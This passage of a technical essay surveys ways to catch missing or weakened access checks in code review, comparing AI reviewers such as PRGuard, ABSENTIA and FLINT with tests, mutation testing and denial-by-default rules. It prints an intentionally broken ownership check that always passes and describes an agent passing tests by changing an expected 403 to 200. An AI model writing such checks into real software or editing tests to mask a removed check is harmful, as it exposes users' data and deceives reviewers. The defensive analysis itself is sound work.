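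The pull request with the unprotected lookup shows why the reason for blocking a change matters. CodeRabbit blocked it, but reported a problem with how the program displayed a secret in the user's browser. If the author fixes only the display, the next review may find nothing to object to, even though the lookup still doesn't enforce project boundaries. The team may then be less likely to check the change again, because it appears to have passed a security review.

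Blocking a change for the wrong reason still has some value, because it delays it and a person who examines the reported problem may notice the real one. That benefit disappears if the author applies the suggested fix and the project merges changes as soon as the tool approves.

The threefold difference is weak evidence of which reviewer is better, because nine of the 14 absence-type cases came from an earlier run of PRGuard itself, using GPT-5.5. The researchers had filtered about 890 candidates from project histories down to about 80, and PRGuard blocked 19 of these. Of the 19, they confirmed 14 by reading the code and 12 with a working attack. They added the 12 to the benchmark, so it contains no flaws from those histories that PRGuard had missed.

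In the comparison, PRGuard used DeepSeek instead of GPT-5.5 but was otherwise unchanged. According to calculations from the paper's figures, this version blocked eight of the nine absence-type cases from the earlier run and only one of the other five. On the 19 pull requests that PRGuard had not selected, it and CodeRabbit each named 12 flaws. The observation that CodeRabbit often blocks for the wrong reason doesn't depend on PRGuard being better, although CodeRabbit might do so less often on other cases.

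The 12 discoveries are nevertheless real vulnerabilities in real projects, and some closely resemble the document site example. In a content management system, the code that updated notifications checked that a user ID in the request belonged to the sender, but then loaded a notification by a separate number that it did not check. Because the notifications were numbered consecutively, anyone who registered could read other people's, including messages with password-reset codes. In a test installation, the researchers used one of these codes to log in as an administrator. A reviewer who looked for an ownership check would have found one, but it covered only the user ID, not the notification.

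### False alarms

A reviewer that blocked everything would catch every missing check, so the number of harmless changes it blocks matters too. PRGuard blocked 5 of the 50 harmless changes in MALPR-BENCH with GPT-5.5 and 4 with DeepSeek. CodeRabbit reviewed only six of them and blocked none. In Pool A, however, GPT-5.5 blocked two of the seven complete fixes and four of the seven incomplete ones, so its verdict was weak evidence of whether a protection was missing.

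Flawed changes are rare, so most alarms can be false even when the false alarm rate is low. With DeepSeek, PRGuard blocked 78% of the 63 flawed changes that it had not discovered itself and that the researchers had not used to develop it, and 8% of the harmless changes. If 10 of 1,000 pull requests had a vulnerability, it would block about 8 of them at those rates, along with about 79 of the 990 harmless ones, so only about one block in eleven would be justified. The real proportion of justified blocks could well be higher, because the harmless changes in the benchmark all involve security code, which is more likely to arouse suspicion than, for example, a new colour scheme.

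Asking a model to justify its answers does not necessarily reduce false alarms. *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?* (Jin and Chen, 2026) tested five models on short programs, each with a description of what it should do. More than 700 tasks each had a correct and a faulty version. The models answered whether the code met the description. In some conditions they also had to explain a negative answer, and in others they had to both explain it and propose a fix. The table shows results for two of the models on HumanEval, one of the three sets of tasks.

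| | Correct code rejected, GPT-4o | Faulty code accepted, GPT-4o | Correct code rejected, Claude 4.5 Sonnet | Faulty code accepted, Claude 4.5 Sonnet |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no only | 26.2% | 2.4% | 26.2% | 2.4% |
| Explain | 58.5% | 0% | 34.1% | 1.2% |
| Explain and fix | 73.2% | 0% | 36.0% | 0.6% |

Both models became stricter when the prompt asked for more. They accepted less faulty code, but GPT-4o rejected almost three quarters of the correct programs. This did not always happen. When Mistral Small 3.1 had to explain its answer on HumanEval, for example, it rejected fewer correct programs and accepted more faulty ones.

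When the models wrongly rejected a program, their explanations most often cited a logic error (48.2%), and 14.1% relied on a requirement that was not in the description. The second mistake would be especially likely in a search for missing checks, because the rule that calls for a check is often in neither the code nor the description. For example, a model might report a missing ownership check in a handler that serves free brochures.

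The tasks were small functions with no particular connection to security, and four of the five models are well behind current ones. Some task descriptions may also have been vague enough that a careful reader would expect more than the correct code provided. The study is therefore weak evidence of how often a current model raises false alarms on pull requests. It is better evidence that the wording of a prompt can affect whether a model misses real flaws or reports ones that don't exist. A team should measure this effect before it adopts a stricter prompt.

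### Whether models could replace human reviewers

In *The End of Code Review*, Monperrus (2026) argues that coding agents should take over most review because they can serve all its purposes more cheaply than people, and because people who must approve large amounts of AI-written code will do so without real scrutiny. The paper presents no new data. Monperrus acknowledges that a model may silently approve a change when an unsure person would admit doubt, and proposes requiring several independent agents to agree and allowing each to answer "I don't know".

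Agreement between agents helps only if they miss different flaws. In Pool A, GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek each failed to name four of the seven flaws, so they must both have missed at least one of the same flaws. PRGuard gave both models the same collected code, and two agents that read different parts of the repository might have fewer misses in common.

Monperrus would keep human approval for high-risk changes and leave routine features, bug fixes and refactorings to agents. But changes that omit or remove a security check often look routine. Sorting changes this way would require recognising the risk before a person reviewed them, and reviewers find that same judgement difficult.

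His doubts about human reviewers have some support. Most participants in the 2021 experiment overlooked the missing check for negative numbers, and people read a diff without the context that PRGuard supplies. But those participants reviewed a different program under different conditions, and none of these studies tested people and language models on the same missing checks.

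## Tools and tests that do not depend on a reader noticing

A reviewer, whether a person or a language model, has to think of a missing check before anyone can add it. A project can rely less on this by putting the rule that the check enforces where a machine can use it. Then, if the check is missing, a test fails, a page stops working or a tool raises an alarm. On the document site, a tool could infer from the other handlers that only owners may read their documents. The project could also put this rule in an automated test or in a list of access rules that the program checks on every request.

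### Inferring the rule from similar code

Suppose the document site has 20 handlers that call `find_document`, and 19 of them compare the document's owner with the user. A tool that counts such patterns can report the twentieth without being given a rule about ownership.

This idea goes back to *Bugs as Deviant Behavior* (Engler, Chen and colleagues, 2001), which treated code as evidence of what its programmers believed. Some beliefs are certain. If one line tests whether a pointer is null and a later line uses the pointer either way, the lines contradict each other, and at least one is wrong. Other beliefs are only probable. If programmers follow a call to `lock` with a call to `unlock` in 999 of 1,000 places, the remaining place is probably an error. The researchers ranked suspected errors by how consistently the rest of the code followed the rule, and found hundreds of errors in the Linux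 and OpenBSD operating systems.

*Chucky* (Yamaguchi, Wressnegger and colleagues, 2013) uses the same idea to look for missing security checks in C and C++. The tool selects the functions most similar to the one under examination, typically 10 to 30, based on the types and functions they use. It then reports conditions that appear in the similar functions but not in this one. It helped the researchers find 12 previously unknown vulnerabilities in Pidgin, a chat program, and LibTIFF, an image library.

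Chucky is less suited to finding weakened checks. Before it compares conditions, it removes negations and replaces comparison operators and numbers with placeholders, so that differently written versions of the same check match. The conditions `quantity <= 100` and `quantity <= 1000000` therefore become identical. A tool that worked this way on Python could still detect that the ownership check had been loosened to "signed in", because the new condition no longer mentions the owner.

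Tools that find missing checks by comparing similar code need most of that code to be correct. If none of the 20 handlers checks ownership, the tool has no difference to report. It also can't assess an operation that occurs only once, because there is nothing to compare it with. If 19 handlers serve private documents and one serves free brochures, the tool would raise a false alarm about the brochure handler, which doesn't need an ownership check. Each time a developer or coding agent copies a handler that lacks the check, the correct handlers look more unusual.

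A language model can infer a developer's assumptions from a single function. *LLM-based Code Auditing by Inferring and Evaluating Developer Assumptions* (Liu and Böhme, 2026) describes CREED, which asks a model what a function does, what its developer must have assumed, whether each assumption is reasonable, and when it could fail. One real function cancelled a payment after checking only the payment's site and status. Its developer apparently assumed that anyone on the same site could cancel it.

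CREED found and correctly explained 39 of 50 recent vulnerabilities. The model CREED uses found 34 when given an ordinary security prompt with its reasoning mode on. CREED produced 7.9 findings for each known flaw it found, compared with 11.3 for the model with the ordinary prompt. By the researchers' count, 21 of the 50 flaws fit no general pattern that a conventional scanner could search for, and CREED found 15 of these.

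CREED reads one function at a time, so it misses protection elsewhere in the code. Of the 13 functions where its first finding was wrong, ten were safe because other code already prevented the problem. It also missed a flaw that let users share files they weren't allowed to download. This broke a rule specific to one application, which someone would have to write down before a tool could check it.

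### ABSENTIA: one route at a time

A model that reads only part of a program can overlook a missing check simply because it never opens the right file. Duarte, Oke and colleagues (2026), in *ABSENTIA*, describe a system that directs a model through an application one route at a time. A route is a web address combined with a method, such as GET for reading or DELETE for deleting. The system works in steps:

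1. An agent identifies the application's framework and its database and login libraries, and works out how the application decides who may see which records.
2. Two agents separately write search patterns for the way this application declares routes, reads requests and checks permissions. A conventional program applies the patterns and builds a graph that links each route to its code.
3. For each route, an agent reads the code and lists the properties that the route should guarantee, for example that only the account that owns an invoice can fetch it.
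4. The agent looks for the code that enforces each property and tries to describe a request that the route would accept but the property forbids. If it can, it reports the property, the relevant code and the request.
5. Other agents look for routes that become dangerous in combination.

The researchers tested ABSENTIA on 30 published access-control flaws from 25 open-source applications, using the versions before and after each fix. The applications had a median of 220 routes. All three configurations below used MiniMax-2.5, a model that an organisation can run on its own machines.

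| | Known flaws found | Average reports per case | Reports confirmed by an AI verifier |
|---|---|---|---|
| Undirected agent | 3 of 30 | 6 | 73.6% |
| Agent sent to each route | 18 of 30 | 119 | 40.5% |
| Full ABSENTIA | 19 of 30 | 77 | 50.8% |

Almost all of the gain came from sending the agent to every route. The undirected agent could take up to 200 turns but used 59 on average, and in 24 of the 30 runs it stopped because it considered the audit finished. The conventional scanners CodeQL and Semgrep found none of the 30 flaws, although Semgrep reported 6,398 other findings.

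In two of its 19 successes, ABSENTIA also reported the flaw in the fixed code, so 17 is a fairer count. Of the 11 flaws it missed, three were in routes that never entered the graph. In the other eight, the agent read the right route but didn't report the flaw. A stronger model, Claude Sonnet 5, found three more flaws when it read the same routes, but a difference that small could be due to chance.

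The tool also gives people many reports to check. One of the researchers checked a sample of reports without knowing the AI verifier's verdicts, and confirmed 42% of those from ABSENTIA and 43% of those from the simpler version that only visits each route. Searching for a forbidden request cut the number of reports by a third, but may not have made the remaining ones more reliable. ABSENTIA assigns its highest confidence to most of its reports, so a maintainer with 77 of them has little idea which to check first. A run cost a median of $44 and up to $316.

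ABSENTIA can reuse its earlier verdicts for routes whose files have not changed. Duarte and colleagues tested this by analysing the fixed version of each application first and the vulnerable version second, which is close to a pull request that deletes or weakens a check. ABSENTIA reported the flaw in 21 of the 30 cases. The median run reused 37% of the earlier verdicts, but eight runs could reuse none.

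### FLINT: a model proposes and a verifier decides

Even a model that reads the right code can accept a check that only looks correct. Yang, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *Suspected Until Inspected*, found an example in a business-intelligence program that lets users delete their access tokens. Moved to the document site, the flaw would look roughly like this:

```python
record = {"owner_id": current_user.id, "number": number}
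if not may_delete(current_user, record): abort(403)
delete_document(number)
```

The code checks whether the user may delete a document that belongs to the user. This check always passes, because the first line fills in the user's own identity as the owner and never looks up the real owner. When the researchers showed the original code to a model, it reported no flaw. When they asked whether anything restricted the deletion, it cited the permission function.

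Their system, FLINT, lets the model suggest which checks protect a page but doesn't trust its judgement:

1. The model lists the functions that answer requests. FLINT collects each one's code and the functions it calls.
2. For each of them, the model writes a certificate. It lists the stored objects that a request can select, what the code does with them, and the lines that restrict the user. The model does not say whether the code is secure.
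3. A conventional program, the verifier, accepts the list of objects as given but tests every claimed check against the code.
4. If no verified check protects an object, the verifier fetches more code and sends the model an objection. The model can cite another check, which the verifier also tests.
5. FLINT also reports a function if at least two similar ones have a stricter verified check.

The verifier traces whether each value comes from the signed-in user, the request or a stored record. It accepts a check only if the check involves both the user and the selected object, ends the request or filters the data on failure, and comes before the access on every path through the code. In the example, nothing in `record` comes from the stored document, so the verifier rejects the check.

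FLINT also assigns levels of authority: 0 for none, 1 for reading, 2 for writing and 3 for full control. An access gets the lowest level of any path to it. In the handler with the preview option, a request that passes the ownership check reaches the file with level 3, but one with `?preview=1` reaches it with level 0. The access therefore gets min(3, 0) = 0, below the 1 needed for reading, so the handler fails by these rules.

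### How well FLINT did

Yang and colleagues ran FLINT on 69 pairs of functions from before and after a published fix. The table gives averages over the 35 projects the functions came from. All the systems used the same model, DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash.

| | Reported the vulnerable version | Reported the fixed version | Told the two apart |
|---|---|---|---|
| FLINT | 85.2% | 27.2% | 62.8% |
| Claude Code | 91.9% | 12.3% | 79.6% |
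| Codex CLI | 97.1% | 22.9% | 74.3% |
| Model asked directly for flaws | 46.7% | 11.1% | 36.7% |
| Model's certificate, mostly believed | 71.0% | 36.9% | 38.8% |

Verification worked considerably better than trusting the certificate, but the two coding agents did better than FLINT. Most of the gap came from repaired code, where FLINT often couldn't verify the new check.

This seems to conflict with the result for ABSENTIA's undirected agent, which found only 3 of 30 flaws. But Yang and colleagues pointed their agents at a particular function, while ABSENTIA's agent had to choose among hundreds of routes. The models and benchmarks also differ, so the comparison is loose, but it suggests that agents judge access checks much better once something directs them to the right place.

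Using FLINT, the researchers also found 112 previously unknown vulnerabilities in 44 of 57 popular applications, and they reproduced each one with two ordinary accounts. In 41 cases the code checked the wrong object, and in 40 there was no check. The rest included checks that relied on an identity supplied by the attacker and checks whose failure didn't stop the request.

For 75 confirmed vulnerabilities, the researchers recorded whether a misleading check was present and whether each system found the flaw for the right reason.

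| | Misleading check present | No check beyond signing in |
|---|---|---|
| FLINT | 18 of 32 (56%) | 27 of 43 (63%) |
| Claude Code | 12 of 32 (38%) | 22 of 43 (51%) |
| Codex CLI | 15 of 32 (47%) | 25 of 43 (58%) |

All three did somewhat worse when something that looked like a check remained. The numbers are small, and the flaws differ. Yang and colleagues found these vulnerabilities themselves, many with FLINT, so the sample may favour FLINT.

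FLINT issued a definite warning for 385 (49%) of the 786 handlers in five whole applications. It ranks its warnings and put 42 handlers in the top group. The researchers read 24 of those and judged eight real or plausible, seven minor and nine wrong. They had also developed FLINT on their own test sets, and its results vary with the model. It distinguished only 29.6% of the pairs with the larger DeepSeek-V4-Pro, partly because that model more often listed no objects to protect.

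### What FLINT can and cannot prove

FLINT clears an access only after showing that every path to it in the analysed code first passes a check involving the user and the selected object. This conclusion depends on five assumptions, not on the model's opinion. One assumption is that a permission function that passes the verifier's tests really decides whether the user may have access.

To test this guarantee, the researchers told a model to get flagged accesses cleared by citing any real code that might pass for a check. The model made 50,903 claims in 34 attempts, and the final verifier cleared no access that the researchers knew to be unprotected. An early version of the verifier had cleared three known flaws in the first attempt, and a later attempt found a gap in a version that the researchers had considered final.

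FLINT can't prove that the model listed every access. In the five applications, about 3% of the cleared handlers called other code that might contain an unlisted access. FLINT also can't identify a rule that the code doesn't reflect, such as a new decision to let accountants read their clients' papers.

### A test that expects a refusal

A project can state such a rule in a test. The following one signs in as Ben and requests a document that belongs to Ana:

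```python
def test_other_customer_gets_403(client):
    number = add_document(owner="ana")
    sign_in(client, "ben")
    response = client.get(f"/documents/{number}")
    assert response.status_code == 403
```

The site also needs a test that Ana can open her own document, because a broken handler that refuses everyone would pass a test that only checks for refusals. Yang and colleagues used similar controls in the attack on access tokens. They confirmed that the attacker could delete their own token and that another page denied the attacker access to the victim's token.

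The refusal test fails if someone deletes the ownership check or loosens it to "signed in". If a developer moves the check into `find_document`, the test still passes, so it avoids the false alarm that a warning about deleted lines would raise. It also passes when someone adds the preview option, because it never sends `?preview=1`.

This test does nothing for a handler that somebody adds next month. A test that goes through every route can cover that case:

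```python
PUBLIC = {"show_brochure"}

def test_strangers_are_refused(client):
    number = add_document(owner="ana")
    sign_in(client, "ben")
    for rule in app.url_map.iter_rules():
        if "GET" not in rule.methods or rule.arguments != {"number"}:
            continue
        if rule.endpoint not in PUBLIC:
            url = rule.rule.replace("<int:number>", str(number))
            assert client.get(url).status_code in (403, 404)
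```

The test requests every page whose address contains only a document number, and fails if Ben, who doesn't own the documents, gets anything other than a refusal or "not found". A new handler without an ownership check makes it fail automatically. So does a new handler for public documents, until the developer adds its name to `PUBLIC`. Omitting the check is therefore no longer enough to make a page public, because the author must also add a line that a reviewer can question.

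Other tools apply the same idea without written tests. They record one user's requests and repeat them as another user. According to Duarte and colleagues, this requires a running copy of the application, an account for every role and a way to put the program in the right state for each check.

### Deleting the check on purpose

A passing test suite doesn't show that the tests would detect the removal of a security check. Suppose a test signs in as Ben, requests Ana's document and confirms only that the server responds. The test runs every line of the ownership check, but it still passes after someone deletes the check.

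Mutation testing reveals this weakness. A developer or a tool makes a small harmful change to a copy of the program and runs the tests. If they all pass, the change "survives" and the tests have a gap. For `show_document`, useful changes include deleting the two lines of the check, loosening the condition, and logging the refusal instead of stopping the request.

A surviving change doesn't always mean the site is vulnerable. If `find_document` also checks ownership, deleting the check from the handler has no effect. Running the tests once for every change can take a long time, so a project might start with the lines that contain `abort(403)`. Mutation testing can't reveal that a check was never written, because there is nothing to delete.

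Yang and colleagues used a similar method to test reviewers instead of test suites. They changed real fixes so that the original attack worked again, by requiring a weaker permission, checking someone other than the caller, or logging a failure and continuing. FLINT reported 24 of 31 such changes, Claude Code 27 and Codex 30. The model that was asked directly for flaws reported 14, including only 4 of the 19 changes that weakened a permission. The researchers found no statistically significant difference between FLINT and either agent.

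A coding agent that can edit both the program and its tests can defeat a refusal test. The pull request might remove the ownership check and contain this change:

```diff
-    assert response.status_code == 403
+    assert response.status_code == 200
```

If a change removes a security check and also alters the tests for that check, all the tests can pass. To prevent this, a project can take the tests that check whether forbidden requests are refused from its main branch, run them against the proposed code, and require approval from someone other than the author when they fail. Legitimate changes to the rules will also need that approval. This does not help when a coding agent adds a new page and misunderstands the rule, because it may write code and tests that make the same mistake.

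### Refusing unless a rule allows it

In the handlers so far, the program grants access unless a line refuses it. A project can reverse this, so that forgetting a rule closes the page. This is denial by default:

```python
RULES = {"about": anyone, "show_document": owner_of_document}

@app.before_request
def enforce_rules():
    rule = RULES.get(request.endpoint)
    if rule is None or not rule(current_user, request.view_args):
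        abort(403)
```

The function `enforce_rules` runs before every handler. It finds the handler's rule, a function that returns true or false, and refuses the request if the rule is missing or returns false. A developer who adds `show_history` without a rule will get a refusal when they first open the page, even for their own document, so a missing rule is harder to overlook than a missing ownership check.

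Denial by default doesn't ensure that the access rule is right. A developer in a hurry, or an agent trying to make a test pass, could add `"show_history": anyone`, though a reviewer would at least see that line in the diff. Denial by default also fails if the rule checks one object and the handler loads another. In one such flaw, a program checked a user ID but then loaded a notification by a separate, unchecked number.

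### Comparing the old and new rules

Once access rules are separate from the rest of the program, a tool can compare two versions of them. The question is the one a reviewer could ask by hand, which requests the new version accepts that the old one refused. Suppose somebody proposes this change:

```python
def old(r):
    return r.is_owner or r.role == "admin"

def new(r):
    return (r.is_owner or r.role in ("admin", "support")) and not r.archived
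```

The new rule looks stricter because it closes archived documents to everyone, but it also lets support staff open other people's current documents, which the old rule did not. A program can find this by trying all 12 kinds of request (owner or not, three roles of customer, support and admin, and archived or not) and reporting each one for which `new(r) and not old(r)` is true. Support staff opening somebody else's current document is the only one it reports. The reverse check finds four kinds of request that the old rule accepted and the new one refuses.

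Real policies can mention names, dates and addresses, which have too many possible values to try one by one. Tools therefore turn both policies into logical formulas and use a solver, a program that either finds a request that satisfies the formulas or proves that there is none. One such check, CheckNoNewAccess in Amazon's IAM Access Analyzer, compares an updated access policy for Amazon's cloud services with a reference policy and reports whether the updated policy allows anything new.

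A result of "no new access" applies only to the two policies compared. It does not show that the old policy was right or that the program checks the policy before opening a file, and it does not cover changes in who holds the support role.

### Which lost checks each method can report

Only the language-model systems in the table have measured detection rates. The other entries are based on how the methods work, and no study cited here counts how many lost checks those methods catch in practice.

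| Method | Never-written check | Deleted check | Weakened check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Comparison with similar code | If most similar code has it | If most similar code has it | Only some changes to the condition |
| ABSENTIA and FLINT | Often | Often | Often, though less reliably for FLINT and the agents when a misleading check remains |
| Refusal test for one handler | No | Yes | If the test sends a newly accepted request |
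| Refusal test for every route | Yes, on the routes it can request | Yes, on the same routes | If the test sends a newly accepted request |
| Mutation testing | No | Shows whether a test would fail | Shows whether a test would fail |
| Denial by default | Yes, the page refuses everyone | Yes, if the whole rule is gone | No |
| Policy comparison | No | Yes, if the check is in the policy | Yes, if the check is in the policy |
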